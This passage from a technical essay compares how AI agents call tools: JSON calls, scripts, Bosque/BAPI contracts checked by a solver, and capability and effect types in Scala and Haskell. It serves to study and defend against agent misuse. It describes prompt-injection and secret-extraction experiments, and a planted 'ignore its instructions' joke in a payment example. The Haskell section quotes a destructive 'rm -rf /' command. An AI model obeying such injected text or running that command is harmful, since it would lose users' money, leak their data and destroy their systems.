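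Varda and Pai also claim that models can handle more tools when the tools are presented as code. Patel and colleagues tested this with 31 requests, first supplying only the relevant functions and then a total of 128. The average score for JSON fell from 83.6% to 81.3%. The average for code rose from 72.6% to 78.1% but was still lower than JSON's.

### Familiarity, execution and precision

Patel and colleagues generated the stubs from the same schemas the models received in the JSON condition. The stubs therefore contained no extra facts about any function, and the results don't show that agents need a more precise specification. The improvements must come from the models' familiarity with code, the way scripts run, or differences between the two prompts.

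Familiarity alone doesn't seem to help much. On simple requests, where it should still help though there is nothing to chain or repeat, the average rose only from 86.1% to 89.5%, and on simple requests from real users it stayed at about 76%. The one large gain, from 73.1% to 83.0%, was in another category of real users' requests.

The test also leaves out most of what makes scripts attractive. The stubs contacted no service and only returned their own arguments. One task asked for the circumference of a circle and then for the perimeter of a square with sides of that length. The circumference function returned only the radius, so the model calculated the circumference itself and passed it on. A model can calculate a circumference, but it has to get the balance of account ACC1001 from the bank. The chaining scores therefore show whether a model can write a plausible sequence of calls, but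 they are weak evidence of whether its script can use the data a real service returns.

Other studies ran the tools, including *HyperTool* (Du, Zhou and colleagues, 2026). It kept every tool's original schema and changed only how the calls ran, by letting the model put several into one block of code. On MCP-Universe, the benchmark Hasan and colleagues used, Qwen3-32B scored 15.7% with ordinary calls and 35.3% with HyperTool. The HyperTool model had extra training on examples of such blocks, but the model still scored 25.5% without it when acting through CodeAct-style code. Because the schemas stayed the same, HyperTool's gain did not come from a new notation for tools.

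With stronger models, the main benefit may be lower cost. Anthropic reports that on a project-management benchmark with 75 tools, programmatic calling cut billed input tokens by about 38% and left accuracy unchanged. On τ²-bench, a test of customer-service conversations with only one or two calls per turn, scores also stayed the same, but costs rose by about 8%. Yang, Yu and Desell (2026), in *When Does Restricting a Coding Agent to execute_code Help?*, replaced the usual file-editing and search tools of two coding agents, Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex, with a single tool for running code. Success rates moved by less than three percentage points. Depending on the agent and the kind of task, cost ranged from 25% lower to 14% higher, though the increase was not statistically significant.

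An agent that writes a script can also commit to a plan too early. *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution* (Felendler, Gandhi and colleagues, 2026) compared the two methods on ten real MCP servers. Scripts needed far fewer tokens and turns for work of similar quality, but they did worse on some tasks that involved three servers. In those cases, the model had typically left out a branch the task needed. An agent that reads each result before making the next call has a chance to notice that it needs that branch.

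### What a script needs to know about results

Scripts do need a more precise description in one respect. With ordinary calls, the model reads a result before it decides what to do next, so it can find the balance whatever the bank calls it. In the script above, the model wrote `account.balance` before it had seen any result. If the bank's field is called `available_funds`, the script fails or, worse, the comparison with 340 comes out false and the payment goes ahead.

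*Beyond Plain MCP* (Rai, 2026) compared three ways for agents to use tools. Rai built a simulated company with 12 servers and 42 tools for billing, calendars, customer records and similar work. Three open models did 119 tasks using ordinary MCP calls, using scripts with tool signatures that described what each tool returns, and using scripts with tool signatures that showed only whether the result was a dictionary or a list. Rai checked the state of the company's data after each task.

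| Model | Ordinary calls | Scripts, results not described | Scripts, results described |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.8-27B | 85.7% | 97.5% | 99.2% |
| Gemma-4-26B | 86.6% | 66.4% | 89.1% |
| Nemotron-3-Nano | 36.1% | 16.0% | 55.5% |

Two of the three models did much worse with scripts than with ordinary calls when the results weren't described. With descriptions, all three did better with scripts, although Gemma's gain was small and could be chance. Patel and colleagues' stubs were equally vague about results, but this did no harm because their scripts had no real results to use.

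Rai wrote the descriptions by hand and refined them on practice tasks, so they may be better than ordinary tool descriptions. The tasks also came from only 21 templates. Still, JSON Schema can express the missing information. If a tool has an output schema, the converter copies the schema's fields into the signature, but tool authors may omit the schema. In Cloudflare's example, a function that lists proposed code changes on GitHub has the output type `unknown`. OpenAI added an `output_schema` field for programmatic calling, and advises developers to have the model call a tool directly if they can't predict the form of its result.

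### What a reviewer gains and loses

A signature is easier to read than a page of JSON, as it is in other compact notations for schemas. But consider how the bank's two tools look side by side:

```ts
get_balance(input: BalanceInput): Promise<BalanceOutput>;
transfer(input: TransferInput): Promise<TransferOutput>;
```

The two lines have the same form, although only `transfer` has an effect. `Promise` means only that the result arrives later. Ordinary TypeScript types and Python type hints describe a function's inputs and outputs but not its effects, which some other languages include in their types. Cloudflare keeps its approval requirement in a separate field beside the signature. That field is optional, so a `transfer` tool converted from MCP runs without pausing for approval unless the developer adds the requirement.

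The script gives a person something that single JSON calls don't, which is the order of the steps and the conditions between them. Anyone who reads a little code can see that the script above pays the plumber only if the account holds at least $340. It helps less when the amounts come from data:

```js
for (const bill of await mail.find_bills()) {
  await bank.transfer({
    amount: bill.amount, payer: "ACC1001", payee: bill.account
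  });
}
```

A reader can tell that this script pays every bill in the mailbox, but not how many bills there are, what they add up to, who gets the money or whether a stranger sent one of them. The user learns the actual amounts only if the runtime stops at each transfer, which brings back the separate confirmation dialogs. The script also can't be reviewed before the agent starts, because the model writes it during the run. If the script fails, the model writes another. Approval of the first shouldn't carry over to the new version, since Felendler and colleagues warn that a malicious tool's error message can influence it.

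Scripts also make more work for programs that supervise agents. *DADL* (2026), which proposes a language for describing companies' tool libraries, points out that a gateway can check each ordinary MCP call against a fixed schema before it runs, but has to analyse code when the agent writes scripts. A client can allow `get_balance` and refuse `transfer` when they are separate tools, but when both are behind a single tool that runs code, only the runtime behind that tool can tell them apart.

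Cloudflare's MCP server for its own services is an extreme case. *Code Mode*, Carey's follow-up to Varda and Pai's post, describes how the server gives agents access to more than 2,500 operations through two tools, `search` and `execute`. Their descriptions take up about 1,000 tokens, while a separate tool for each operation would bring the total to 1.17 million, more than a model's context could hold. Each tool accepts a single string called `code`, so the schema for `execute` is the same whether the agent lists a customer's firewall rules or changes them. To know beforehand what the agent could do, a person has to look at the permissions that Cloudflare asks the user to approve when the agent connects.

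## The case for contracts that people can read and programs can check

In TypeScript, `transfer` and `get_balance` look alike, and the bank's rules about amounts and approvals end up in comments or in the server's code. Marron, a computer scientist at the University of Kentucky, wants the tool's specification to contain such rules, in a form that people can read and programs can check. Marron's language for writing these specifications, BAPI (short for Bosque API), builds on Bosque, a programming language Marron designed to make code easy to reason about.

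*Toward an Agentic Infused Software Ecosystem* (Marron, 2026) gives the example of a function declared as `wait(duration: Int)`, which doesn't specify whether the whole number is in seconds or milliseconds. An agent has to guess, spend a step reading the documentation, or keep the documentation in its context from the start. The declaration `wait(duration: MilliSeconds)` specifies the unit and uses almost the same number of tokens. A type checker can also enforce this unit by rejecting a program that passes seconds, which it can't do if the unit is only mentioned in a JSON `description` string.

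Marron (2024) argues in *Toward Programming Languages for Reasoning* that people, language models and checking programs struggle with the same features of ordinary programming languages, for different reasons. People get tired and take shortcuts, so they miss special cases. A checking program misses nothing in the code, but it can't take into account that a number is a temperature unless the code specifies it. A language model fills gaps in the text with whatever was likely in its training data. If this is right, writing a fact into the specification instead of leaving it to convention helps all three.

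### The transfer tool as a contract

Adapted to the transfer tool, Marron's payment contract looks roughly like this:

```
type USD = Decimal;
type AccountId = CString of /'ACC'[0-9]{4}/c;
enum Status { completed, pending }
entity Receipt { field transfer_id: String; field status: Status; }

%% Pay the payee from the payer's account. Use only when
%% the user has asked for a payment.
api transfer(amount: USD, payer: AccountId, payee: AccountId): Receipt
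    env={
        PAYMENT_TOKEN: OAUTH_TOKEN,
        PAYMENT_LIMIT: USD
    }
    permissions={ \account:${payer}\ }
    requires 0.0<USD> < amount;
    requires amount <= env.PAYMENT_LIMIT ||
        $events.contains(Approve{|payee=payee, amount=amount|});
;
```

It is about as long as the TypeScript version. The first line creates a decimal type that a program can't confuse with other decimals. Amounts carry their type, as in `340.00<USD>`, so a script that passes euros or a bare number fails the type check. The type also specifies whether the amount is in dollars or cents, though a model could still enter the wrong amount. The `AccountId` line does the same job as `pattern` in the JSON, and the two lines that begin with `%%` are prose for the model and the person to read.

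`env` lists values that must come from the caller's environment, here the token that authorises payments and the user's payment limit. Marron writes a fixed $100 limit into a simpler draft of the contract, then replaces it because a constant can't follow changes in business rules or users' needs. With `PAYMENT_LIMIT`, the same contract works for a user who allows $50 and for one who allows $5,000.

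`permissions` lists the resources that the tool may use, written like web addresses. A pattern with wildcards can cover a group of them, such as all the files in one temporary folder. Marron (2025), in *Trustworthy-by-Construction Agentic APIs*, prefers this to the special permission languages of older systems, such as Java's Security Manager, which developers have found hard to understand. The only address listed here is the payer's account. The payee's balance will change too, but Marron separates permission from physical effect. A customer paying a plumber needs power over the customer's own account but not over the plumber's. In one place, Marron's prose mistakenly describes the tool as confined to the payee's account, although the contract names the payer's. This slip is a small argument for contracts, since a runtime would enforce only the code.

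This line could also stop the tool from sending the user's account details to an attacker, which the bare signature did not rule out, but only if something enforces it. Bosque's own runtime can do so. For a tool written in C on Linux, according to Marron, enforcement may require a virtual machine or remain partial. If the tool runs on the bank's servers, the customer has to trust the bank to comply with it.

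The two `requires` lines are preconditions. The first excludes zero and negative amounts, because a negative payment might take money from the payee. The second allows a payment if it is within the limit or if the event log, `$events`, contains the user's approval of that amount for that payee.

### What the event log adds

Only the runtime can add entries to the log, and it records events in order, based on what API calls returned. An agent therefore can't invent an approval to satisfy the precondition. Checking the log also doesn't depend on any outside system. If a program instead looked up the user's approval on a remote server, the answer could change between the check and the payment.

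A condition on a balance would have that problem. An earlier version of the contract, in Bosque's *data specifications* (2024), required the payer's balance to cover the amount. Later versions drop this condition. Marron doesn't explain why, but a balance can change at any moment, and the bank has to check it anyway.

Specialists have long used temporal logics, which have operators for ideas such as "always" and "eventually", to write rules about the order of events. Marron instead uses ordinary code over a list of events, partly because classical temporal logics can't express some useful rules, such as that an agent must release as many cloud machines as it has started. The other reason is readability. Marron reports that developers already think of such rules as conditions on a series of events, based on interviews and conversations with them while working at Microsoft and Morgan Stanley.

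The log can also appear in postconditions, which begin with `ensures`. In an example based on a Morgan Stanley demonstration, a tool for renting sailboats may report success only if the log shows that it checked the day's weather and reserved the boats. So a reader of the contract learns what the tool does as well as what it needs. `transfer` has no such postcondition, and Marron acknowledges that its preconditions could allow a single approval to cover the same payment twice.

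Some rules are only preferences. Bosque's meeting scheduler, for example, has a "soft" condition that the time should fall within everyone's working hours. The condition guides the agent's choice, but a user who wants a call at 10 p.m. can presumably still have one.

### Rules that belong to the data

A contract on `transfer` protects one tool. When many tools use the same kind of data, attaching the rules to the data type makes more sense. Bosque's example is a weather service that returns a low of 28, a high of 34 and a wind speed of `"5 to 10 mph"`. A program has to read a separate field, `"units": "si"`, to interpret the temperatures. Marron's typed version declares the temperatures as Fahrenheit, splits the wind speed into two numbers in miles per hour, and restricts percentages to between 0 and 100.

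This example also shows how a typed specification can go wrong. Marron's version types temperatures as Fahrenheit but keeps a `units` field that still accepts `si`, so a metric forecast would pass every check despite the contradiction.

An invariant is a rule that every value of a type must obey. Marron's later temperature range has the invariant `$low <= $high`, so no program can create a range whose low is above its high. Bosque checks active invariants whenever code creates or updates a value. Rules that take more computation to check can go under the keyword `validate`, which is for data that arrives from outside. In a trading application that Marron ported from Morgan Stanley's sample code, the stock on hand must never be negative. Outside data must also pass two `validate` checks: no two orders may share an identifier, and the starting stock minus all orders must equal the remaining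 stock.

The keyword `sensitive` marks data that shouldn't leak. In Marron's example, an order contains a taxpayer identification number of a sensitive type. When a program writes the order to a log or a crash report, BAPI by default replaces the number with asterisks. Marron's runtime environment, Mint, also checks that no public address returns sensitive data, and it can quarantine the output of an agent that has read sensitive data.

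Other systems can keep using JSON. BAPI generates the JSON form of a value from its type, along with the code to read and write it, and is designed so that converting a value to JSON and back returns the same value. This is hard because JSON has no native form for dates or many kinds of identifier, and many programs lose digits when they read whole numbers above 2⁵³. BAPI also has its own shorter notation, which leaves out field names because the type already supplies them. An order might be written as `Order{'A53', 45.50d, '123456789'}`.

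According to Marron, BAPI can also generate OpenAPI descriptions, so a company could adopt it for its own tools without waiting for everyone else. Clients that read only the generated description would miss conditions such as the one on the event log. Clients of a Mint server can see these conditions because the server's `/actions` address lists the tools the caller has permission to use, with their signatures, conditions and comments. Other addresses offer usage examples and a search function, so an agent doesn't have to load everything at once.

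### Checking a script before it runs

Mint checks preconditions when a call happens, and it aborts the task if one fails. By then, a script may already have done things that nobody can undo. Marron's checker, Sundew, examines the whole script beforehand. In the main example, a user asks an agent to pay a friend, Tom, half of a restaurant bill mentioned in a message. The agent might write:

```
action splitBill(message: String, friend: AccountId) {
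    let share = agent Chat::compute<Option<USD>>(
        env{}, message, "How much is half of this bill?"
    );
    if(share === none) {
        return fail("The message contains no amount.");
    }
    api transfer(env{...}, share, env.account, friend);
}
```

The script asks a second language model to work out the amount from the message. It gives that model an empty environment, `env{}`, so the model can't see or leak the payment token. The model must return either a dollar amount or `none`. If lunch cost $45.50, Tom should get $22.75. But the amount could be higher, either because lunch was expensive or because Tom added a joke telling the model to ignore its instructions and pay him $1,000.

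Sundew translates the script and the contract into logical formulas and passes them to an SMT solver, a program that either finds values that make a formula true or proves that none exist. The solver can't know what the second model will answer, so it treats the amount as an unknown, *s*. The user's limit, *L*, and the event log, *E*, are unknown as well. The solver then looks for a case in which the script reaches the transfer and one of the preconditions fails:

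*s* ≤ 0, or (*s* > *L* and *E* contains no approval of *s* for Tom)

One such case is a limit of $100, an empty log and a model answer of $200, which leads the script to attempt a forbidden payment. The solver therefore finds that the amount can exceed the limit and that the script never asks for approval. The first half of the formula can also be true, because the model might answer with zero or a negative number, but Marron's sample messages mention only the limit.

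Marron expects this to give an agent better feedback than a failed test would. If a test fails because a $200 payment broke a $100 limit, the agent might respond by refusing every payment of $100 or more, even for users with a higher limit. The solver's result supports a more general message, that the amount may exceed whatever limit the user has set. The agent can then add a step that asks the user to approve payments over the limit, and run the check again. It could also run the checker while it is still writing the script. In the proposal's longer version of the script, about half the code comes after the transfer, so an agent that checked only at the end would have written all of that code on top of a faulty plan.

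The check covers only what is in the contract. If Tom jokingly asks for $90 and the limit is $100, the payment meets every condition, and Tom gets too much. The contract limits the loss from such semantic misuse but doesn't prevent it. Sundew also works only on code written in Bosque. The JavaScript that models write for Cloudflare's Code Mode could still get precondition checks at run time, but Sundew couldn't analyze it in advance.

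Marron calls the bill-splitting script hypothetical. Extending the checker to event logs was still a task in the research proposal in September 2025. The February 2026 paper describes how the extension works, with the log as another input to the formula, but gives no timing for a script that uses a log.

### Why Bosque avoids loops and mutation

Programmers have had verification tools for decades, but most either need an expert's help or work only on restricted questions, largely because of two common features of programming languages.

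Loops are one feature that makes programs hard to check automatically. Suppose a script loops through a list of bills to add them up. To prove something about the total for a list of any length, a checker needs a loop invariant, a statement that remains true after every pass, and no general method can find one for every loop. Languages such as Dafny and Lean let a programmer supply the missing steps of a proof. Bosque instead removes loops. Programmers process lists with ready-made operations such as `allOf`, which tests whether every element meets a condition, or `map`, which applies a function to each element. These operations have direct counterparts in the solver. Marron estimates that such operations can handle more than 90% of the work that loops do on collections.

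The other is mutation, or changing existing data. If a function can alter data that other parts of the program also use, a checker has to work out after each call which of its earlier conclusions still hold. Bosque's values never change. Programmers can still reassign variables for convenience, but the compiler turns each assignment into a new definition. Bosque also fixes details that other languages leave open, such as the order in which a sort places equal items, so that the same input always gives the same result.

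A function written under these rules is already close to a logical formula. One that returns −1 for negative numbers and 1 for all others becomes, slightly simplified:

```
(define-fun sign ((x Int)) Int
  (ite (< x 0) (- 1) 1))
```

Here `ite` means "if, then, else". Sundew needed 7 milliseconds to prove that the result lies between −1 and 1 for every whole number.

Lists are still difficult because the solver will eventually find an error that some list can trigger, but may search forever if there is no error. Sundew therefore limits the length of the strings and lists in the input. Bosque's *small models* (2025) illustrates this with lists of at most three elements. The elements can have any value, so this covers far more than a set of tests. With the length limited, the solver can finish and return either an input that causes the error or a proof that no input within the limit does.

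Bosque's *Compactly Solvable Languages* (2025) contrasts this with bounded model checking, an older automatic method that limits how many times the checker follows a loop. That method can miss a simple input that makes the program repeat a loop many times. Sundew instead limits the size of the input, so it covers every small input, however long the program takes to process it.

The approach depends on the hypothesis that a small input can trigger most bugs. Two of Marron's examples support it. The checker found that the trading application accepted an order for −1 items and increased the stock. In a small database, it found that the code for adding a row didn't check the row's length. It also refuted the claim that removing a row always makes a table shorter, because the table may be empty. The error there was in Marron's specification, not the code.

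The hypothesis is less reliable for rules that involve counting. Suppose a bank allows five payments a day. If the checker considers only histories of up to three events, it can't detect that a script might make a sixth payment. A developer can raise the bound, but the search then takes longer.

### What Marron has measured

The best published evidence for the checker is a set of three small programs in Marron's proposal. Sundew's predecessor in the Bosque toolset went through every possible error in each program's own code, without any hints from a person:

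| Program | Lines of code | Possible errors checked | Total time | Longest single check | Errors found |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Trading application | 900 | 6 | 50 ms | 12 ms | 0 |
| Ray tracer (draws 3D scenes) | 1,500 | 15 | 422 ms | 54 ms | 1 |
| In-memory database | 1,800 | 24 | 1,359 ms | 135 ms | 1 |

The line counts include Bosque's own library code. At these speeds, an agent could check a script several times while writing it, and most agent scripts are much shorter than these programs. But none of the three is an agent's script, and none calls outside tools or reads an event log. According to Bosque's post from the same month, the solver was slower than Marron wanted, especially when there was an error to find, and slower than an earlier prototype.

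There is less evidence that contracts help agents succeed. Marron reports that Gemini-2 and GPT-4 were roughly 20% more successful at writing code that used the payment API in Bosque than in TypeScript, even though they had no training in Bosque. In another experiment, feedback from the checker raised the success rate for agents' top three plans by more than 20%. Marron calls both results preliminary, and they appear in a proposal, which has to make its subject look promising. Marron doesn't state how many tasks there were or whether the gains are in percentage points, and doesn't show the TypeScript version.

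The first result is surprising, if it holds up, because Varda and Pai's argument implies that models should do better with TypeScript, which is far more common in their training data than Bosque. The Bosque version in that comparison was only the signature with the `USD` type, before Marron added any preconditions. The gain would therefore be evidence for named types, but not for permissions or the event log.

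An older example from Marron shows how a contract might help. GPT-4 was given the vague task of completing a function that finds the "largest pair" of values from two lists. In TypeScript, its first answer took the largest value in the first list and the value at the same position in the second. The Bosque version added two postconditions and one worked example. GPT-4's top answer was still wrong, but it failed the worked example, and the next one passed. The additions helped mainly by letting a program reject a wrong answer without having to interpret the request.

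The newer results in the June 2026 tool paper concern testing the tools themselves. Tecton, a test generator, takes a BAPI specification and uses a language model to suggest realistic values. According to Marron, its tests ran 70% to 90% of the lines of code on standard benchmarks and exposed two to four times as many faults as leading fuzzers, which are programs that test software with many generated inputs. Each test suite cost less than $0.10 in model fees. This gives tool authors a reason to write precise specifications even if no agent ever reads them. The paper contains no new figures on how well agents do with BAPI. In the proposal, Marron planned to translate the tools of AppWorld, a benchmark in which agents operate various simulated apps, from JSON Schema into BAPI and compare the results. That experiment would provide much better evidence of whether BAPI helps agents than the preliminary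 figures do.

### Whether abler models will need contracts

One objection is that designing a language around the weaknesses of today's models is wasted effort, because those weaknesses are temporary. A sufficiently capable model might work out on its own that a duration is in milliseconds, read all the documentation without losing track, and notice that a payment looks too large.

Marron replies by imagining a model as capable as a programmer in the top 10% worldwide. Marron thinks such a programmer would benefit from units in types, explicit limits and automatic checks, since many of these features address mistakes that good programmers make now. As an example of experts making expensive mistakes with payments, Marron cites a bank's accidental transfer of $900 million, which the bank blamed on human error. Some tasks also need to succeed almost every time, and few people would accept a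 1% chance that an agent stops paying their mortgage. The checker doesn't depend on who wrote the script, so it would work just as well if a new kind of AI, or a person, replaced today's language models.

The reply is more convincing for some parts of the contract than for others. It shows that experts would gain something from explicit units, but the gain may shrink as models get better at inferring them, and Marron has no measurements of how it changes with ability. The payment limit, however, has to be written down, because it is the user's decision. No model, however capable, can infer from a tool's signature that this user wants to approve any payment above $100. If the limit is in a contract, the bank or the user can enforce it without judging how capable the model is.

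## The case for types that track side effects, permissions and data flow

Marron's contracts can limit how much an agent pays and to whom. But somebody has to write the conditions, and Sundew needs a solver and a language without loops to check scripts against them. Several research groups proposed a lighter check in 2026. The agent still writes a program, and a checker still examines the whole program before it runs. But this checker uses only types, which record what kinds of thing the program may do, such as reading a balance, sending money or writing a file, and sometimes where its data may go. Passing this check is far from proof that the whole plan is right. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) argue in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* that precise specifications of an agent's behaviour are often unavailable or impractical, and call types "a lightweight middle ground".

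### An effect type for the payment script

An ordinary type checker works out what kind of value an expression produces. An effect system also works out what running the expression may do. Its conclusions have this form:

Γ ⊢ *e* : *τ* ! *ε*

Given the variables and tools listed in Γ, the expression *e* produces a value of type *τ*, and running it has at most the effects in the set *ε*. As an example, take the script that pays the plumber only if the account holds at least $340, in simplified notation:

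```
let account = get_balance("ACC1001") in
if account.balance < 340 then "not paid"
else transfer(340, "ACC1001", "ACC2002").status
```

Suppose Γ gives `get_balance` the effect `Bank.read` and `transfer` the effect `Bank.pay`. The checker needs three rules. A call has the effects of its tool, a sequence has the effects of all its steps, and an `if` has the effects of both branches, because either could run.

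| Part of the script | Type *τ* | Effects *ε* |
|---|---|---|
| `get_balance("ACC1001")` | Balance | {Bank.read} |
| `account.balance < 340` | Boolean | {} |
| `"not paid"` | String | {} |
| `transfer(…).status` | String | {Bank.pay} |
| The whole script | String | {Bank.read, Bank.pay} |

If the agent's job is just to report on the account, its environment can allow only {Bank.read}. The checker then rejects this script before it runs, even if the account holds $12 and the script would never have made the payment.

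*ε* does not include the amount. A script that sends $34,000 to a stranger has the same type and effects, so a checker that accepts one script accepts the other. The main objection to effect types is that they are coarse, so a harmful call can be well typed. The systems below address this in different ways, and none relies on effects alone.

As with Sundew, a rejected script leaves nothing to undo. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a follow-up to Odersky's work, gives the example of a model whose code subtracts 50 from a balance of 100 and then returns text instead of the new number. The compiler rejects the code as a whole, so the balance is still 100 when the model tries again. This protects only against mistakes the compiler can detect. If a well-typed script makes two payments and the bank refuses the second, the first has still gone out.

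### Capabilities as variables in Scala

TACIT is an MCP server built at EPFL, a technical university in Lausanne, by the group of Martin Odersky, who designed the programming language Scala. Any agent that supports MCP can send it Scala code. TACIT compiles the code with capture checking, an experimental Scala 3 feature that tracks capabilities in types, and runs the code only if it passes the check.

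In this system capabilities are ordinary variables, and the type of every function lists the ones it holds:

- `String -> Int` holds no capabilities, so it can only compute. Programmers call such a function pure.
- `String ->{log} Unit` can use the file `log` and no other capability. (`Unit` means that it returns nothing of interest.)
- `String => Unit` may hold any capabilities at all.

The part in braces, the capture set, plays the role of *ε* in the formula. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) accordingly describes capture checking as "a lightweight effect system". A capture set names particular objects, though, so `{log}` stands for this one file and not for file writing in general. This is precise, but a capture set can't name a whole category of capabilities or exclude one. The paper proposes classifiers, which would allow both.

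Capture sets also help with secret data. In TACIT's version of a bank's tools, a request for recent transactions returns a value of type `Classified[List[Transaction]]`. `Classified` is a sealed wrapper, and the agent's code can work on its content only through the method `map`, which accepts only pure functions:

```scala
val history: Classified[List[Transaction]] =
  getMostRecentTransactions()

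// Accepted: the function only adds up numbers.
val total = history.map(ts => ts.map(_.amount).sum)

// Rejected: the function also holds the file log.
history.map(ts => log.write(ts.toString))
```

The second function has the type `List[Transaction] ->{log} Unit`. `map` requires a plain arrow with no capture set, so the compiler rejects the program. The first function compiles, but `total` is itself classified, so the agent can't leak the sum either. Odersky and colleagues call this local purity, because the restriction applies only to the code inside `map`. The rest of the script can still write files and use the network.

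A sandbox that controls which files and websites a program may reach can't make this distinction. An agent may have good reasons to read a private contract and to call a hosted language model, so the sandbox permits both. The leak occurs when the agent includes the contract's text in the call.

When a script prints `total`, TACIT shows the user the actual figure in the terminal but puts only `Classified(****)` into the model's context. If a language model must read classified text, for example to summarise a contract, the script can pass the text to a second model that the user trusts, perhaps one on the user's own computer. That model's reply is also classified.

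Capabilities can also expire. A script that needs a folder requests access for one block of code, and the compiler rejects any attempt to return a function that could still use the folder after the block ends. The types control whether a piece of code can use the file system and for how long, while the library checks paths at run time and rejects any outside the folder.

### What the compiler takes on trust

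Capture checking fails if code can hide which capabilities it holds. A type cast, which tells the compiler to treat a value as having a different type, can stop the compiler from tracking a capability. Reflection, which finds and runs code by name while the program is running, can do the same. In Scala's documentation, *Safe Mode* describes a restricted version of Scala that excludes these features and is meant for code that agents write. Zhao and colleagues point out that without safe mode, a script that holds no capabilities could still use reflection or start another program. Safe mode was at first available only in the compiler's nightly builds, the daily test versions, according to VirtusLab's *Safe Scala an introduction*.

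Agents may use only libraries that are themselves safe. But a library that sends email or calls a bank has to contain unsafe code somewhere, so its programmer can mark it `@assumeSafe`, and the compiler then accepts it without checking. Scala's example is an email function for agents that prompts the user to confirm each message and then calls an ordinary mailer. The compiler doesn't verify the confirmation step, so if somebody deleted it by accident, every script that passed the compiler's checks before would still pass them.

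The safety of TACIT's payment tool can depend on how its wrapper is declared. The tool's published signature, `sendMoney(recipient: String, amount: Double, subject: String, date: String): MessageResult`, doesn't mention a capability. Scala attaches a method's capabilities to the object that contains it, so a reader has to look there. If the wrapper's author marked that object as safe but forgot to declare that it uses the network, the compiler would treat `sendMoney` as pure and allow it inside `map`. A script could then put classified details in the subject line of a payment.

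JSON tools require the same trust in the server's code. Typed systems reduce the amount of code to trust. Odersky and colleagues put the reusable part of TACIT at about 1,000 lines, and the typed wrappers for each of their customer-service domains at a few hundred more. People can review that code once, whereas an agent writes new scripts on every run.

Some leaks remain even if the library is correct. An agent could leak one bit of a secret by making a computation take longer when that bit is 1. Exceptions can also carry information out of pure code. Tracking every possible division by zero in types would be impractical, so Scala relies on the surrounding program to catch exceptions. Types also don't constrain what an external program does once a script starts it, so Odersky and colleagues advise allowing only specific commands.

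The type of `sendMoney` is also coarse, because it accepts any recipient and any amount. TACIT reduces the danger by passing transactions and files to the agent's model only in classified form, so the model never reads instructions that an attacker has hidden in them. This does not protect against an agent that gets the amount wrong.

### What the Scala experiments measured

Odersky and colleagues tested whether secrets would leak by giving agents a software project with a folder of passwords, keys and confidential documents. They combined 12 ordinary tasks with 10 prompt injections, which are instructions planted in material the agent reads. They also added 11 requests in which the user tried to extract the secrets, either by asking directly or by posing as someone with authority. They ran each trial once with the secrets wrapped in `Classified` and once with the secrets in plain text.

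| | Sonnet 4.6, wrapped | Sonnet 4.6, plain | MiniMax M2.5, wrapped | MiniMax M2.5, plain |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No leak, 120 injection trials | 100% | 100% | 100% | 97.5% |
| No leak, 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% | 100% | 27.3% |
| Ordinary tasks done correctly | 99.2% | 83.3% | 90.0% | 88.3% |

The type system is meant to guarantee the perfect scores, so they mainly confirm that TACIT works as designed. The plain-text columns show how much the models' training already prevents. Injections almost never worked, and most leaks came from MiniMax when the user asked for the secrets. The wrapper didn't stop the agents from doing their work. Sonnet's low score with plain text may come from the set-up, because the model often ran out of time or turns and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection.

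The team also tested TACIT on AgentDojo, a standard benchmark for prompt injection, using two models and 1,926 attacks in total. In the one attack counted as successful, the agent booked the right hotel but quoted a review that recommended a different one, which TACIT's rules allow. With OpenAI's o4-mini, TACIT completed 52.9% of office tasks, while CaMeL, an earlier defence that tracks data while a program runs, completed 81.4%. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT completed 64.3% of travel tasks and CaMeL completed 1.4%. Odersky and colleagues describe the number of tasks the two systems completed as comparable, but that understates how much the results vary.

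Another objection is that agents may struggle to write the language, since models have few examples of capture checking to learn from. On τ²-bench, however, three models did slightly better with Scala than with ordinary tool calls in both domains tested, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. The compiler rejected between 0.3% and 7.9% of their code, depending on the model and domain, and the models usually fixed it in one or two more attempts. On SWE-bench Lite, MiniMax fixed 125 of 300 bugs with TACIT and 130 without it.

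The τ²-bench result is weaker evidence than it looks because the tools have ordinary types and no capture sets, as in `cancelReservation(reservationId: String): Reservation`. The test mostly shows that models can write typed Scala. The bug-fixing test used capabilities more, but the team ran it with only one model.

Zhao and colleagues' own results are less encouraging. In LACUNA, DeepSeek-v4-flash solved 76.0% of 392 τ²-bench tasks, compared with 90.0% using ordinary tool calls. The paper calls this "on par", but the gap is 14 points overall and 22 in the retail domain, where the compiler rejected 22.4% of the model's code. In the telecom domain, it rejected 89% of the code from a weaker model, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite. Types aren't the only possible cause, because LACUNA code also directs the agent's loop and can call the model again, which makes it harder to write than a script that calls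 a few tools. None of the rejected code ran, so the mistakes led to extra attempts and unfinished tasks.

### Result types in Haskell

Haskell has recorded effects in ordinary result types for decades. Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, use this in a library called ELBA. It provides a function, `agent`, that asks a model for a Haskell program, checks the program against the type that the surrounding code expects, and then runs it. A public calculator could expect a whole number:

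```haskell
answer :: Int
answer = agent mathTools userRequest
```

A visitor might ask it to delete every file on the server and then compute the factorial of 5. If the model obeys, it will write something like `do system "rm -rf /"; return (factorial 5)`. ELBA rejects this program because of how Haskell treats input and output:

1. A function that interacts with the outside world returns an action, whose type begins with `IO`. The function `system`, which runs a shell command, is one of these.
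2. Combining an action with other steps gives a larger action, which also has an `IO` type. The program above has the type `IO Int`.
3. Safe Haskell code has no function that turns an `IO Int` into an `Int`.
4. A program of type `Int` therefore can't run any action, whatever the visitor asked for.

Haskell puts the earlier formula's *ε* inside *τ*. A program of type `Int` may mention an `IO` action and discard it, but then the action never runs. Zhou and colleagues therefore slightly overstate the rule when they write that any part with an `IO` type gives the whole program an `IO` type. A Haskell program of type `Int` can also divide by zero or run forever, although they list exceptions among the things that `Int` excludes.

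Step 3 depends on a safe subset of the language, because full Haskell includes `unsafePerformIO`, which does what the step rules out. Safe Haskell, an existing compiler setting, excludes this function and similar features.

Most agents need some effects. A developer can define a new action type that offers only approved operations, and hide the means of constructing certain values. Zhou and colleagues do this for an agent that compiles bibliographies. Adapted to the bank, the tools could have these types:

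```haskell
getBalance :: AccountId -> BankIO Balance
askUser    :: Payment -> BankIO (Maybe (Approved Payment))
transfer   :: Approved Payment -> BankIO Receipt
```

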